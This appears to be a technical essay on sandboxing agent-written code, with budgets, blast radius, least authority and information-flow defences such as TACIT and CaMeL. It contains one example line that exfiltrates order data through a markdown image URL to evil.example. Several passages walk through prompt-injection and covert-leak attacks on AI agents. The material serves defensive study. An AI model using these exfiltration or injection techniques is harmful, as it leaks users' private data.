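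Wasmtime's *Struct Config* recommends writing slow host functions asynchronously, so that a waiting call returns control to the host, and putting a timeout around the whole run. Cloudflare's limit on processor time also excludes waiting, and Cloudflare sets no time limit on individual subrequests. A Dynamic Worker with a 10-millisecond processor limit can therefore stay open for minutes unless the host adds its own timeout.

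Memory needs limits both inside and outside the sandbox. Inside, Wasmtime by default lets a module's memory grow to the maximum the module declares, so the host has to configure a lower one. Outside, the host uses its own memory when it copies arguments. If a program passes a reason 50 million characters long, a host that copies the text before checking its length has already used the memory to hold it. For programs built in its newer component format, Wasmtime limits the data transferred in one call through a separate allowance, confusingly called "hostcall fuel". The default is 128 MiB, far more than `flag` needs. The allowance resets with each call, so a host that keeps the data from ten calls could hold ten times as much.

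The stack limit covers only the stack space that Wasm code uses. Host functions run on the same thread and can exhaust the rest. According to Wasmtime's documentation, this typically aborts the whole process, which on a server would end other users' requests too. The risk arises when a host function recursively processes nested data, because the program controls the nesting depth. `flag` avoids this risk by accepting only two strings.

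Output limits protect the model's context as well as the disk. At four characters per token, a program that prints a megabyte would add about 250,000 tokens to the model's next step. But a hostile program could exploit a log limit by filling the log before it acts. Cloudflare, for example, stops adding to the Worker's logs for a request after 256 KB. The host should therefore record calls to `flag` in a separate log that the program's own messages can't fill.

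If `flag` returns a promise, `orders.forEach(o => flag(o.id, "late"))` starts every call without waiting for any reply. With 2,000 orders, that puts 2,000 calls in flight, all competing for the shop's database at once. Cloudflare queues the seventh outgoing connection until one of the first six gets a reply, but it says calls through service bindings don't count towards that limit, so the host needs its own queue for them.

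Whether gas covers compilation depends on the design. With QuickJS inside metered Wasm, the parser is part of the module, so parsing a huge program uses gas. With V8, or with a new Wasm module for each script, the engine compiles the program before its code starts running, so gas does not cover that work. A maximum program length, perhaps 50 KB, is a simple precaution.

One suggestion in a May 2026 discussion on Wasmtime's issue tracker was to control the overall budget across repeated runs by giving a program only as much fuel as it may use in one burst, then checking a broader rate limit each time that fuel runs out. Retries can also cost money. Varda and colleagues give a list price for Dynamic Workers of $0.002 per unique program loaded, so 1,000 attempts would cost $2, plus the much larger bill for the model.

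### How one Wasm program can slow a whole machine

The agent's program on the order page can reach the disk only through `flag`. Many Wasm programs on servers get broader access through WASI, a standard set of functions for files, clocks and other system services. Yu, Zhan and colleagues (2025), in *Exploring and Exploiting the Resource Isolation Attack Surface of WebAssembly Containers*, examined how much damage such access permits. They tested Wasmtime 24.0.0 with WASI, and Wasmer 4.3.2 with WASIX, an extension that adds network connections and other features. They first used both engines' source code to trace which operating-system calls each interface function can lead to. Then they ran programs that used those functions heavily and measured the disk speed, network speed and idle processor time that remained.

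The programs did severe damage while using very little processor time. In one Wasmtime test, the process used 0.09% of the processor while the disk's read speed fell from 456 megabytes per second to 0.04 megabytes per second. In a Wasmer test, a process that used 2.7% of the processor cut the available network bandwidth from 875 megabits per second to about 62. Programs like these spend nearly all their time waiting for the operating system, so they would take a very long time to use up their gas.

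The usual accounting also missed part of the load. When a Wasmtime program repeatedly forced file data onto the disk, its process used about 10% of the processor, but the machine's idle time fell by about 25 percentage points. Yu and colleagues attribute the difference to work in other parts of the operating system that Linux doesn't charge to the program. The amount of uncharged work may be smaller than this difference, because dstat, which they used to measure idle time, lists time spent waiting for the disk separately. The test machine also had a mechanical hard disk, which handles many small operations less well than the solid-state drives common in servers. Still, the slowdown was more than 99%, so it could be much smaller on better hardware and still be serious.

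Yu and colleagues' first two mitigations use existing Linux features. The XFS file system can cap how much space and how many files a program's directory may hold. Control groups, or cgroups, limit a process's processor time, threads, disk traffic and network traffic, though the host must set them up before it starts the Wasm engine. Neither limits the work that Linux attributes to other parts of the system. Yu and colleagues therefore also suggest limiting how often a program may trigger sensitive system calls, and monitoring kernel resources with eBPF, which runs small checking programs inside the Linux kernel. The permitted rates would have to suit each application, which is difficult for a general container service but fairly easy for a host whose programs all do similar work.

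Yu and colleagues dismiss fuel for long-running servers because ending a server abruptly interrupts its service. A ten-line script that runs once doesn't have that problem. Their disk results do apply to the order page, because a database usually forces each completed change onto the disk. A loop of `flag` calls can therefore produce a similar load, even though the interface doesn't involve files.

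Wasmtime's developers have since added limits on some of these interfaces. In February 2026, NVD's *CVE-2026-27204 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, described how programs could exhaust a host's resources through WASI. GitLab's *CVE-2026-27204* (2026) lists the possible effects, which include crashing the host's process and making it allocate arbitrary amounts of memory. The fixed versions of older releases keep the new limits loose by default to avoid breaking existing programs. Version 42 and later set them tightly by default. Operators who stay on an older release therefore need to install its fixed version and tighten the limits themselves.

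### A stopped program leaves its changes behind

When the gas runs out, Wasmtime raises a trap, an error that ends the program at an exact instruction. The trap does not undo host calls that have already finished. Suppose the order page uses the surcharge of 2,000 units, and 150 late orders are spread evenly through the list. The program stops after flagging 78 of them. An employee looking at the page sees plausible flags and no sign that the other 72 are missing.

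Missing flags do little harm, but stopping other tasks partway can leave the data in an invalid state. A program that moves ten items of stock between warehouses might subtract them from one and run out of gas before adding them to the other. The program can't repair this itself because the trap prevents all its remaining code from running, including any `finally` cleanup block.

If the host times out a slow database call, the database may still complete the change a moment later, so for a while the host can't determine whether the order has a flag.

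The host could pause the program instead of ending it, and grant more gas if the program has been making progress. This helps if the limit was slightly too low, but not if the program crashes or has a bug, so the host still needs a way to handle half-finished work.

| Remedy | If the program stops midway | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Collect proposed changes, then apply them | The host discards the proposals | The program doesn't see the effect of its own changes |
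| Run the program inside a database transaction | The database undoes the changes | Other users may have to wait, and outside effects remain |
| Make each operation safe to repeat | A second run completes the work | Wrong changes from the first run remain |
| Check the whole program before running it | No help once the program has started | The check finds only certain errors |

#### Collecting changes and applying them together

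For the order page, collecting the changes takes only a few lines in the host:

```
const proposed = new Map();

const flag = (id, reason) => {
  checkArguments(id, reason);
  if (!proposed.has(id) && proposed.size >= 150) {
    throw new Error("too many flags");
  }
  proposed.set(id, reason);
};
```

If the program finishes normally, the host checks that the orders are still open and saves all the flags in one database operation. If the program runs out of gas, the host discards the flags. Holding the flags until the end also removes most of the problem of deciding how much gas a call to `flag` should use, because each call now takes microseconds instead of 20 milliseconds. The disadvantage is that `flag` can report success for an order that a colleague ships before the host saves the flags, so the host has to tell the model afterwards which ones it saved.

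Applying the list can fail halfway too. Cloudflare's experimental file library for agents, shell, undoes the earlier writes in a batch when a later one fails. According to Cloudflare, a program can also preview the result with the `dryRun` option, or set `rollbackOnError: false` to keep the writes that succeeded. The host may want to prevent agent-written code from turning rollback off. Rollback covers one batch at a time, so if a program applies two plans and stops between them, the first plan's writes stay in place.

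#### Transactions and repeatable operations

With a database transaction, the host opens the transaction before the program starts, makes every `flag` write inside it, and commits only if the program finishes. The program can read its own changes, which helps when later steps depend on earlier ones, as in the stock example. However, the database may block employees from editing the affected orders while the program runs. That is tolerable for three seconds but not for a program that pauses for hours to await approval. A transaction also can't recall an email the program has sent. On the order page, the host can use both methods by collecting the flags first and then opening a short transaction to save them.

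Some effects can't wait for the end or join a transaction, and for these the host should make repetition harmless. Setting a flag twice is already harmless, but adding a note twice produces two notes. The host can give each effect a fixed identifier, such as the task number combined with the order id, and skip any effect it has already carried out. Cloudflare recommends designing long-running Workers so that interrupted work is safe to retry, because crashes and routine updates can end a program even when it stays within its limits.

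Retrying completes the job only if the second program makes the same changes as the first, but an agent often rewrites the program before retrying. If the first program flagged the wrong customers because of a reversed comparison, a corrected version will flag the right ones but leave the wrong flags in place. The host should list the completed calls in its error message so the model at least has a record of what to undo.

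#### Checking the program before it starts

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) prevents some partial effects by rejecting faulty programs before they run. A developer writes `agent[T](task)` where a Scala program needs a result of type `T`. The model writes code for the task, and the Scala compiler checks that code as if the developer had typed it there. If the check fails, none of the code runs, and the model gets the compiler's error messages so it can try again. The same check can restrict which capabilities the code uses.

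In one example, a balance is 100, and the model has to subtract 50 and return the new number. Its code subtracts 50 but returns a sentence instead of the number. An ordinary JavaScript host would detect the wrong result only after the subtraction. LACUNA rejects both lines together, so the balance stays at 100.

The guarantee applies only to rejected programs. Code that passes the check can still select the wrong orders, fail halfway because the database is down, or exceed a budget. Zhao and colleagues state that types cannot express fuel, time or memory, and their experiments limited these separately. In simulated customer-service conversations, each task had at most 200 steps, 500 tool calls and 300 seconds of inactivity.

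With DeepSeek's V4 Flash model, the compiler rejected 8.6% of programs in a test on difficult research questions and 22.4% in the retail part of the customer-service test. Many of those programs would have failed before changing anything, so the check probably prevented partial effects in a much smaller share. Across all 392 customer-service tasks, LACUNA solved 76.0% with this model and an agent that makes ordinary tool calls solved 90.0%, though Zhao and colleagues describe the two as on par. The gap was smaller with a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, where LACUNA solved 29.1% and the tool-calling agent 33.2%. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen less Scala than Python in training, in which case a check for a more familiar language might reduce the solve rate less.

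The order page could get a similar but weaker check by running the TypeScript compiler on each program. This check would catch a misspelled `daysOpen` before the loop started, which would save a run. But it would add little protection against partial effects, because a host that collects proposed flags already discards them if the program fails.

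## Blast radius: the most that hostile code could do

The blast radius of a run is everything that a hostile program could read, change, send or use up with what the host gave it. Once the host's developers have fixed the proxies and budgets, they can assume that an attacker will write the program and work out the blast radius before a model writes any code.

More exactly, let R₀ again be the references that the host injects and B the budgets for gas, host calls, memory and output. Let E(p) be the effects of running program p with R₀ and B in an engine that works correctly. Then:

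BR(R₀, B) = { E(p) : p is any program the engine accepts }

The blast radius is a set of possible outcomes, because a budget forces the attacker to choose which actions to take. With a cap of 99 flags, a program could flag any open order but not all of them.

The definition excludes engine bugs, which call for a second barrier behind the engine. It also excludes how careful the model is, because that affects only how likely a bad run is. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (Jarmak, 2026) discusses an incident in which the same failure could reach both a database and the data for recovering it, and notes that a warning in the prompt does not remove any of an agent's capabilities.

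*Bounded Agents* (2026) offers a formula for agents that delegate work to other agents. Each resource r has a score from 0 to 1 for the damage it could add, and each agent p has a ceiling β on the total:

BRmax(p) = { r in p's scope : score(r) ≤ β(p) − what p has already used }

An agent can't pass on more scope or budget than it has, so a helper's blast radius never exceeds that of the agent that started it. The scores make different resources comparable, but somebody has to choose them. For a host with two proxies, listing the effects is easier.

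### Permission and authority

On the order page, the program may call `readOrders` and `flag`. In Miller's terms, these are its permissions, and the blast radius is its authority, meaning whatever it can bring about by using them.

Miller and Shapiro illustrate the gap between permission and authority with a Unix password file. Bob has no permission to read the file, but Alice does, and she sends him copies, so Bob has the authority to read it. The access settings alone don't show this, because it depends on how Alice behaves. Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues later proposed formal definitions of both terms in *Permission and Authority Revisited* (2016), with separate bounds for what a program can do now and what it might eventually be able to do.

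A program's authority can extend well beyond the function it calls. Suppose the shop's warehouse software holds back every flagged order until an employee clears the flag. The agent's program can then delay 99 shipments, even though `flag` contains no shipping code. If someone adds that rule later, the blast radius grows without any change to the sandbox. The host's developers therefore have to count how people and other software react to each effect, as well as the effect itself.

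### The order page in numbers

If the gas limit is 200,000 units and each flag carries a surcharge of 2,000 units, the program can raise at most 99 flags. It can still read all four fields of all 2,000 orders with a single call to `readOrders`.

If `reason` is free text of up to 200 characters, 99 flags can hold 19,800 characters that staff or another model will read. A hostile program could write that a customer has phoned to change the bank account for a refund. It could also write instructions to a model that summarises the flags each morning.

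Free text can also carry data. Each character can be any of 95 printable characters, so it holds about 6.6 bits. The total, status and age of one order fit into 30 bits (20 for a total of up to about €10,000 in cents, 2 for the status and 8 for the age), so the whole list takes 60,000 bits. If packing the data uses 50 units of gas per order, the program has 100,000 units left, enough for 49 flags. The reasons in those flags can hold 9,800 characters, or about 64,000 bits. The program could therefore copy the whole list, except the ids, into the reasons, and anyone able to read the flags could unpack it.

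Allowing only four fixed reasons shrinks this a lot. Each reason code carries 2 bits, so 99 codes carry at most 198 bits. The choice of which orders to flag carries more. If all 2,000 orders are open, there are about 2⁵⁶⁴ ways to choose 99 of them, so the choice carries about 564 bits. If only 600 are open, it carries 383 bits, which together with the codes could reveal the details of about 19 orders. Someone who can also see the sequence in which the flags arrived could learn up to 518 bits more.

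The gas limit and the surcharge leave one gap. `readOrders` has no surcharge, so a program that calls it in a loop at 5 units per pass could make the host copy the list 40,000 times. The host should cap these calls too, perhaps at three per run.

The same hostile program could do far more under `eval`:

| | Sandbox, free-text reasons | Sandbox, four codes | `eval` on the order page |
|---|---|---|---|
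| Read | Four fields of 2,000 orders | The same | Everything on the page, including customers' emails and the session token |
| Change | 99 flags with up to 19,800 characters | 99 flags with fixed wording | The page, and anything the shop's server lets the employee do, such as refunds |
| Send | The flags and the program's result | The same, but the flags carry far less | Anything, to any server the browser can contact |
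| Use up | 2 ms of computing, 2 s of database time, three copies of the list | The same | The page's thread until someone closes the tab, and as many requests as the server accepts |

The damage under `eval` can also continue after the tab closes, because a stolen session token works until it expires.

### The argument for least authority

The principle of least authority is to give each program only the authority its task needs. Miller and Shapiro's example is the card game Solitaire, which needs to draw in its own window, respond to the player and perhaps save a game to one file. Ordinary operating systems also let it read the player's email, and it could sell what it finds without breaking any of the system's rules.

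The case for the principle rests on six premises:

1. A program can do harm only through the operations and budgets it has received.
2. The host hands over only what the task needs.
3. Operations that are acceptable one at a time are also acceptable together.
4. A host function that acts for the program uses the host's power only as the host intended.
5. The program's influence ends at the edge of the sandbox.
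6. The program's access ends with the task.

If all six conditions hold, hostile code can do no more harm than the task makes unavoidable. An engine bug would break the first condition, but the other five can fail even if the engine works perfectly.

### Exposing more than the task needs

Developers rarely know in advance what a task will need, and if they grant too little access, the agent fails. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) tested a coding agent on 37 repair tasks, running each five times. The agent completed 97% of the runs with full access but 21% with only a short initial list of files and commands, because many tasks legitimately required something next to the listed files.

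A developer who sees 21% will probably widen the list, and the quickest way is to expose everything. For example, an employee using the order page might ask for late orders by country. The developer should add only the country field to the copy, but returning the whole customer record takes less typing and prevents further complaints about missing fields.

### The lethal trifecta

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) describes three useful abilities that are dangerous in combination: access to private data, exposure to text an attacker may have written, and a way to communicate with the outside. An agent with all three can follow instructions in the attacker's text to collect the private data and send it out. GitHub's official MCP server combined all three. It could read public issues that anyone can file, read private code, and create pull requests that exposed what it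 had read.

Two additions to the order page, each of which would pass review on its own, could together let an attacker see the totals of other customers' orders. One developer exposes the delivery notes so that the agent can find gift orders. Another adds `replyToCustomer(id, text)`, which can write only to the customer who placed the order. An attacker then places an order, uses the delivery note to ask for the totals of all other open orders, and receives them in the reply.

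A host can check for such combinations automatically whenever somebody adds a function. *When Safe Skills Collide* (2026) lists ten forbidden combinations, such as access to credentials together with outgoing communication. The paper uses simulated attacks to test separately for exposure to an attacker's text, because that exposure isn't a property of a function. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) extends the problem to several agents, where one may read the data and another may send it. Its method analyses the permissions without running anything, so a match is a reason to review the configuration, not proof of an attack.

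Models have become better at resisting planted instructions. Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* describes an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned of Claude Code, its programming agent, in auto mode, where software rather than the user approves the agent's actions. None of 720 attacks on three Claude models succeeded, but the attacks came from only 72 scenarios, and a real attacker can devise others. Willison suggests a software package whose instructions tell the agent to run a second package before the tests, and the second package then steals the data.

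### The confused deputy

A host function always has more power than the program that calls it, because otherwise the program wouldn't need it. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes how a user turned this power against its owner at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time.

Tymshare's compiler collected usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operating system let it write to any file there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. The compiler also let users name a file for debugging output. One user gave the name of the billing file, and the system let the compiler open it because the compiler had permission to write there. The debugging output replaced the billing records.

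The user had no permission to access the billing file but had the authority to destroy it through the compiler. Hardy attributes this to the compiler having authority from two sources, Tymshare and the user, and no way to specify which to use for a particular file. He proposes giving the compiler a capability for the statistics file and having the user supply one for the output file. A user who can't write to the billing file would then have no capability for that file to pass to the compiler.

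The order page would repeat Tymshare's mistake if it gave the program a function `saveReport(name, text)` that writes to the shop's shared folder. The program could pass `prices.csv` as the name and overwrite the price list. If the host instead injects an object for one new file, whose only method is `write(text)`, the program cannot choose which file it writes to.

Many functions still have to accept plain values, such as the order id in `flag`, or an amount and an account number. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines how LangChain (with LangGraph), LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit handle such values. All three limit which functions a model can call, but by default none checks whether the values in a call are permitted before running it. In a demonstration with simulated payments, LangChain's normal code carried out a call that changed a merchant's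 payout account to an attacker's.

Mellafe Zuvic's checking program, ScopeGate, refused the same call because the account wasn't on a list written by the operator. It also stopped 48 prepared attempts to bypass it and 29 attempts by a model that learned from each refusal. An earlier version had a flaw that would be easy to repeat in a JavaScript host. A check such as `if (amount > 500) throw` lets NaN through because `NaN > 500` is false. The host should require a finite number within a range.

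The list has to come from a source the model can't influence. *The Stochastic Deputy* (2026) treats the model as the confused deputy, since it acts with the user's authority on text that outsiders can shape, and it can't reliably tell instructions from data. The paper concludes that a security argument must not assume the model acts correctly. Mellafe Zuvic reports that in simulated attacks on 27 models, cheaper models attempted the forbidden action 60% of the time on average, and flagship models 19%.

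Checking values doesn't catch every misuse, because a program that flags the wrong open order still passes every test that `flag` makes. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk give the first formal definition of a program's freedom from confused deputy attacks. They relate it to information-flow integrity, which concerns whether untrusted data can influence trusted actions. If a delivery note on the order page influences which orders the program flags, untrusted data has influenced a trusted action, even if every id is valid.

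### Results as an exit

The interpreter has no network access, but its results leave the sandbox. The host passes the program's return value and printed output to the model and often shows them to the employee.

Suppose a chat panel beside the order page displays formatted text, and the program returns this:

```
"![chart](https://evil.example/c.png?d=" + packedOrders + ")"
```

The panel treats the text as an image, so the employee's browser requests it from the attacker's server, with the order data in the address, even though the program never called `fetch`. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork had a similar vulnerability. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* traces it to emails and Teams messages that the agent could send without approval. According to Willison, the agent could send these to the user's own inbox, and they could contain external images. When the user opened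 a message, it could send an attacker links for downloading the user's files without a login.

The model that reads the output may also have tools that the program lacks. If the agent can send email through an ordinary tool call, the program can print a request to email the list to a certain address. *AgentTrap* (2026) includes such a test, in which a diagnostic script prints a follow-up instruction unrelated to the user's task. A cautious host therefore assumes that the model will follow any instruction in the output, and counts everything the model's other tools can do as part of the blast radius.

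Even a choice between permitted actions can reveal data. In July 2026, Willison described a trick by Ayush Paul against the Claude chat application. The application could open only addresses that came from the user, a search or a page it had already fetched. Paul's website offered one link per letter of the alphabet and asked the model to find the user's profile by following them. The sequence of links the model followed spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic fixed this by no longer letting the model follow links from fetched pages.

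*Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, 2026) shows that a malicious tool can leak a secret one bit at a time through permitted requests. The tool sent a request when a bit was one and sent nothing when it was zero. In one configuration, the receiving server recovered all 64 bits of the secret from 64 calls.

### Access and data that outlast the task

Each run could leak about 19 orders, so an attacker who keeps getting new delivery notes in front of the agent could copy the whole list in roughly a hundred runs.

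Data that survives between runs makes leaks easier. Aun and colleagues ran 51 attacks by malicious tools three times each, behind a filter that allowed contact only with approved servers. One tool kept a salary sheet from an earlier call and attached it to its next permitted request. With the filter alone, data leaked in 51 of the 153 runs. Starting a fresh process for every call reduced this to 15. Some leaks remained partly because a single call could still contain data meant for different recipients.

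Starting a fresh interpreter doesn't remove anything the program has left outside it. In another *AgentTrap* test, a script creates a hidden file of instructions that can influence the agent's later sessions. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) describes a slower attack, in which an add-on plants an instruction in the agent's long-term memory. A later request from the user reactivates the instruction, and the agent sends out passwords or keys. Free-text reasons on the order page could work the same way if the agent reads old flags at the start of a new task.

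Permissions can also accumulate across tasks. On Monday the host exposes the delivery notes for one task, and on Tuesday it adds `replyToCustomer` for another. If it withdraws neither, the agent has the lethal trifecta, although neither task needed all of it. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) advises developers to tie permissions to the current task instead of to an agent's lasting identity.

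Santos-Grueiro calls such leftover access "lingering authority" and built PORTICO, a program that stands between a coding agent and its tools, to remove it. In the paper's main example, the agent has to add a timeout setting to two related files:

1. A contract written beforehand states what the agent can use at the start, what it may request later, and what stays forbidden. The agent starts with the first file, its test and the command that runs the test.
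2. The agent requests the second file. PORTICO checks the request against the contract and issues a handle, a reference that works only for that file, for the permitted kind of use, and while the grant lasts.
3. The agent reads and edits the file through the handle.
4. PORTICO runs the tests. When they pass, it cancels the handle and removes it from the options the model sees.
5. If the agent tries the old handle again, PORTICO refuses before anything happens.

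Only a trusted event, such as a test result or a decision by an authenticated person, can extend or end a grant. The model can't extend one by giving a good reason, or end one by announcing that it has finished.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same grants at the same moments but never cancelled them. Both completed all 10 runs. When the agent tried to reuse its access afterwards, PORTICO always refused and the other version always allowed it. PORTICO also blocked all six scripted attempts to write through an old handle, while the other version allowed them all. The outcome was the same in six cases with a live model, covering file changes, version control and network access. The tests confirm that cancellation works as designed, but they don't measure how often agents misuse old access in practice.

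The paper also reports a blast radius, a weighted count of the sensitive resources that each run reached or changed. Across 17 scenarios with tempting but forbidden resources, it averaged 6.65 with full access, 4.09 in a coarse sandbox, 2.73 with a fixed list of permitted tools, and 0 with PORTICO. The score measures what the agent did, which may be much less than the worst it could have done. The contract that PORTICO enforced also defined what counted as a violation, which makes its zero less impressive.

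The protection reduced the number of completed tasks. On the repair tasks, PORTICO completed 161 of 185 runs, compared with 180 for the fixed list. In additional tests on real software projects, it completed 31 of 42 cases, while the version that never cancelled grants completed all 42. Some contracts ended access too early or provided no way to renew it. In the main test on real projects, no forbidden actions occurred under any method, even full access, so the evidence for a safety benefit comes from the constructed scenarios.

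Starting a new interpreter for each program has much the same effect as cancelling handles, provided the host decides for each request which proxies it needs. The model's context can also carry information between tasks, so if Tuesday's task should not involve Monday's delivery notes, the host has to start it with an empty context.

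## Preventing leaks through permitted operations

Proxies control what a program may read and which functions it may call. They don't control what happens to data in between. Suppose the employee wants to know which late orders come from the same customer. A developer adds the field `email` so that the program can compare customers. The courier company can see the reasons attached to flags. A program can now do this:

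```
for (const o of orders) {
  if (o.daysOpen > 7) flag(o.id, o.email);
}
```

The host permits both reading and flagging, but a program can combine them to send customers' email addresses to the courier. The lethal trifecta is a special case of this gap, but a careless program can cause the same leak without an attacker. A filter in `flag` that rejects the @ sign wouldn't help much, because a program can reverse the address or replace the sign.

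*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao et al., 2026) points out that ordinary sandboxes miss this kind of leak because the data flows between permitted calls without crossing the sandbox's boundary.

### Rules on where data may go

Information-flow control is a set of rules on where data may go after a program has read it. Each piece of data carries a label. A confidentiality label records who may see the data, and an integrity label records which sources have influenced it. Suppose there are two marks, *secret* and *untrusted*, and a label is a set of them. An order id has the empty label, a customer's email address has {secret}, and a delivery note has {secret, untrusted}. Two rules do most of the work:

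label(f(x, y)) = label(x) ∪ label(y)

a call may receive v only if label(v) ⊆ the marks that the call accepts

Text that combines an order id with an email address is therefore also secret. `flag` doesn't accept marked values, so it rejects this text, but a function that shows text to the employee could accept it.

The rules also have to cover conditions. The line `if (o.email.startsWith("a")) flag(o.id, "late")` puts no part of the address in the flag, but anyone who sees the flag learns that the address starts with "a". The ideal is noninterference, which means that if two runs differ only in their secrets, anyone without permission to see those secrets observes the same results from both.

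### How TACIT checks a program before it runs

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) comes from a group in Lausanne that includes Martin Odersky, the designer of the programming language Scala. An agent sends TACIT a Scala program through an MCP tool call. The Scala compiler either rejects the program with error messages or lets it run. The program can access files, other programs and the network only through a small library.

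In most languages, a function's type describes its input and output. Scala's capture checking, an experimental feature, adds the capabilities that the function can use:

```
String -> String         // uses no capabilities
String ->{file} String   // can use the capability "file"
String => String         // can use any capability
```

The compiler works out a function's capabilities from its body, so an agent can't hide one by leaving it out of the type. A function that uses no capabilities is *pure*. It can compute a result but can't print, write to a file or contact a server.

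Sensitive data arrives in a wrapper called `Classified`, and the program can't take it out. The program can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the data and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions, so the code that sees the data can't send it anywhere.

A program gets access to files by calling `requestFileSystem` with a directory and a block of code, and it can use the directory only inside that block. If the program tries to return a function from the block that would read a file later, the compiler rejects it, because the function's type would have to mention a capability that exists only inside the block. Redell's caretaker would stop this leak only at runtime, when the program called the function.

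Scala also has features that get around its own type system. A cast, for example, tells the compiler to treat a value as a different type, which could make a function that writes to a file look pure. TACIT's restricted language mode, called safe mode, forbids unchecked casts, reflection (looking up and calling code by name at run time) and global functions that might have hidden effects. According to the project's public page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, a validator enforced these rules in March 2026 by searching for forbidden patterns, and the developers planned to switch to the compiler's own safe mode. Until they do, the guarantee partly depends on the list of patterns being complete, and incomplete lists were a recurring problem in vm2.

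Finally, TACIT separates what the agent sees from what the user sees. If a program prints a classified summary, the user's terminal shows the text, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. The summary stays wrapped in later turns, so a program can compute its length for the user without revealing the number to the agent. For tasks that require reading classified text, such as summarising a contract, the program can pass the text to a separate trusted model that has no tools and whose answer comes back wrapped.

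#### A program that the compiler rejects

In one of the tests, an agent tried to print an access key. This is a simplified version:

```
requestFileSystem("secrets") {
  val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  key.map { k => println(k) }
}
```

Printing requires an output capability, so the function passed to `map` has the type `String ->{io} Unit`, where `Unit` means it returns nothing useful. But `map` requires `String -> Unit`, which allows no capabilities, so the compiler reports an error and the program never starts. The compiler would accept `key.map { k => k.trim }`, which removes spaces and returns another wrapped text.

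The same rule would stop the leak on the order page. If `email` were classified and `flag` required a capability, `o.email.map { e => flag(o.id, e) }` wouldn't compile. A version that only tests the first letter wouldn't compile either, because the function would still use `flag`.

A function inside `map` can put the secret into an error message, so TACIT catches such errors and turns them into ordinary values, which it can also wrap.

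### What the safety test measured

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a directory of API keys, confidential documents and a database. Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 each ran the same 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them in plain text. In 120 of the trials, the researchers paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 planted instructions. In the other 11, the user made a malicious request. Five of these requests asked for secrets openly, and six pretended to come from someone with authority, such as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency.

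With the wrapper, neither model leaked a secret in any trial. Without it, 98.5% of Sonnet's trials and 91.6% of MiniMax's had no leaks. Sonnet leaked secrets in response to two of the requests that claimed authority. MiniMax leaked secrets in eight of the 11 malicious trials and three of the 120 others.

The planted instructions were a weak test of the wrapper, because they rarely worked even without it. Most of the difference between runs with and without the wrapper comes from the 11 malicious requests, and a system with a 20% leak rate could plausibly get through 11 trials without a leak. The trials mainly confirm that the software had no obvious flaw. The compiler is a better reason to trust TACIT, because it applies its rule to every program, regardless of why the model wrote it.

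Odersky and colleagues also ran AgentDojo, a public benchmark that hides instructions in the bank records, work files, chat messages and travel data that an agent reads. TACIT blocked the attack in all but one of 1,926 trials. In the exception, a planted hotel review recommended a different hotel from the one the user wanted. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counted the other hotel's name as a successful attack. TACIT's rules allowed the agent to quote the reviews because they were public.

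### How CaMeL tracks data while the program runs

Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) in 2025. It builds on a defense against prompt injection that Willison proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). In that design, a privileged model plans the work from the user's request and never reads untrusted data, which is handled by a quarantined model with no tools.

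Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how CaMeL puts this into practice. The privileged model writes its plan as a program in restricted Python. For a gift order, the plan might be:

```
note = read_note("A-1042")
gift = ask_quarantined("Does this note ask for gift wrap?", note, bool)
if gift:
    flag("A-1042", "gift")
```

CaMeL's interpreter runs the plan and labels each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, a short Python function that allows or refuses the call based on the arguments and their labels. If the delivery note contains an instruction to email the customer list somewhere, the instruction may influence the quarantined model, but that model can only return true or false. The plan has no step that sends email, and text in the note can't add a step to the plan.

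TACIT does not protect the plan this way. Unclassified text that its agent reads can influence the next program the agent writes, and the compiler only ensures that the program stays within its capabilities. On the order page, a planted instruction could still make a TACIT agent flag the wrong orders, whereas CaMeL would have fixed the steps before reading the page.

The most recent measurements are in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), for which Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues built a version of AgentDojo where several agents share the work. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of trials without CaMeL and 0.2% with it. The benefit varied greatly by model. Without CaMeL, 36.1% of attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1 and none against GPT-5.5. However, *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports that OpenAI's own automated attacker consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences.

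### What happens to labels in a conversation

Odersky and colleagues argue that run-time tracking like CaMeL's cannot keep a value's label once the value enters the model's context as ordinary language. If a program prints a customer's complaint and the model later writes a sentence based on it, no interpreter can trace that sentence back to the complaint. TACIT avoids this problem for classified data by never showing that data to the agent.

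The CaMeL team doesn't seem to have answered this criticism directly. The criticism has limited force within a single plan, because CaMeL's privileged model doesn't see the values. It matters more when a result becomes part of a later request. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include CaMeL co-author Ilia Shumailov, found such a loss between agents. In their example, one agent gets a list of job applicants from a database and tells another to send a summary to a colleague. Someone has planted a database entry asking for a copy to go to an outside address. The first agent treats that entry as untrusted data but includes the summary in its instruction to the second agent, which reads the whole instruction as a trusted request and sends the copy. Every attack that still worked against CaMeL in their benchmark used this route.

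Their remedy splits each call between agents into a message and a set of named values. The receiving agent's privileged model reads only the message, and the interpreter rejects any message that contains tool output. With this change, none of the attacks succeeded.

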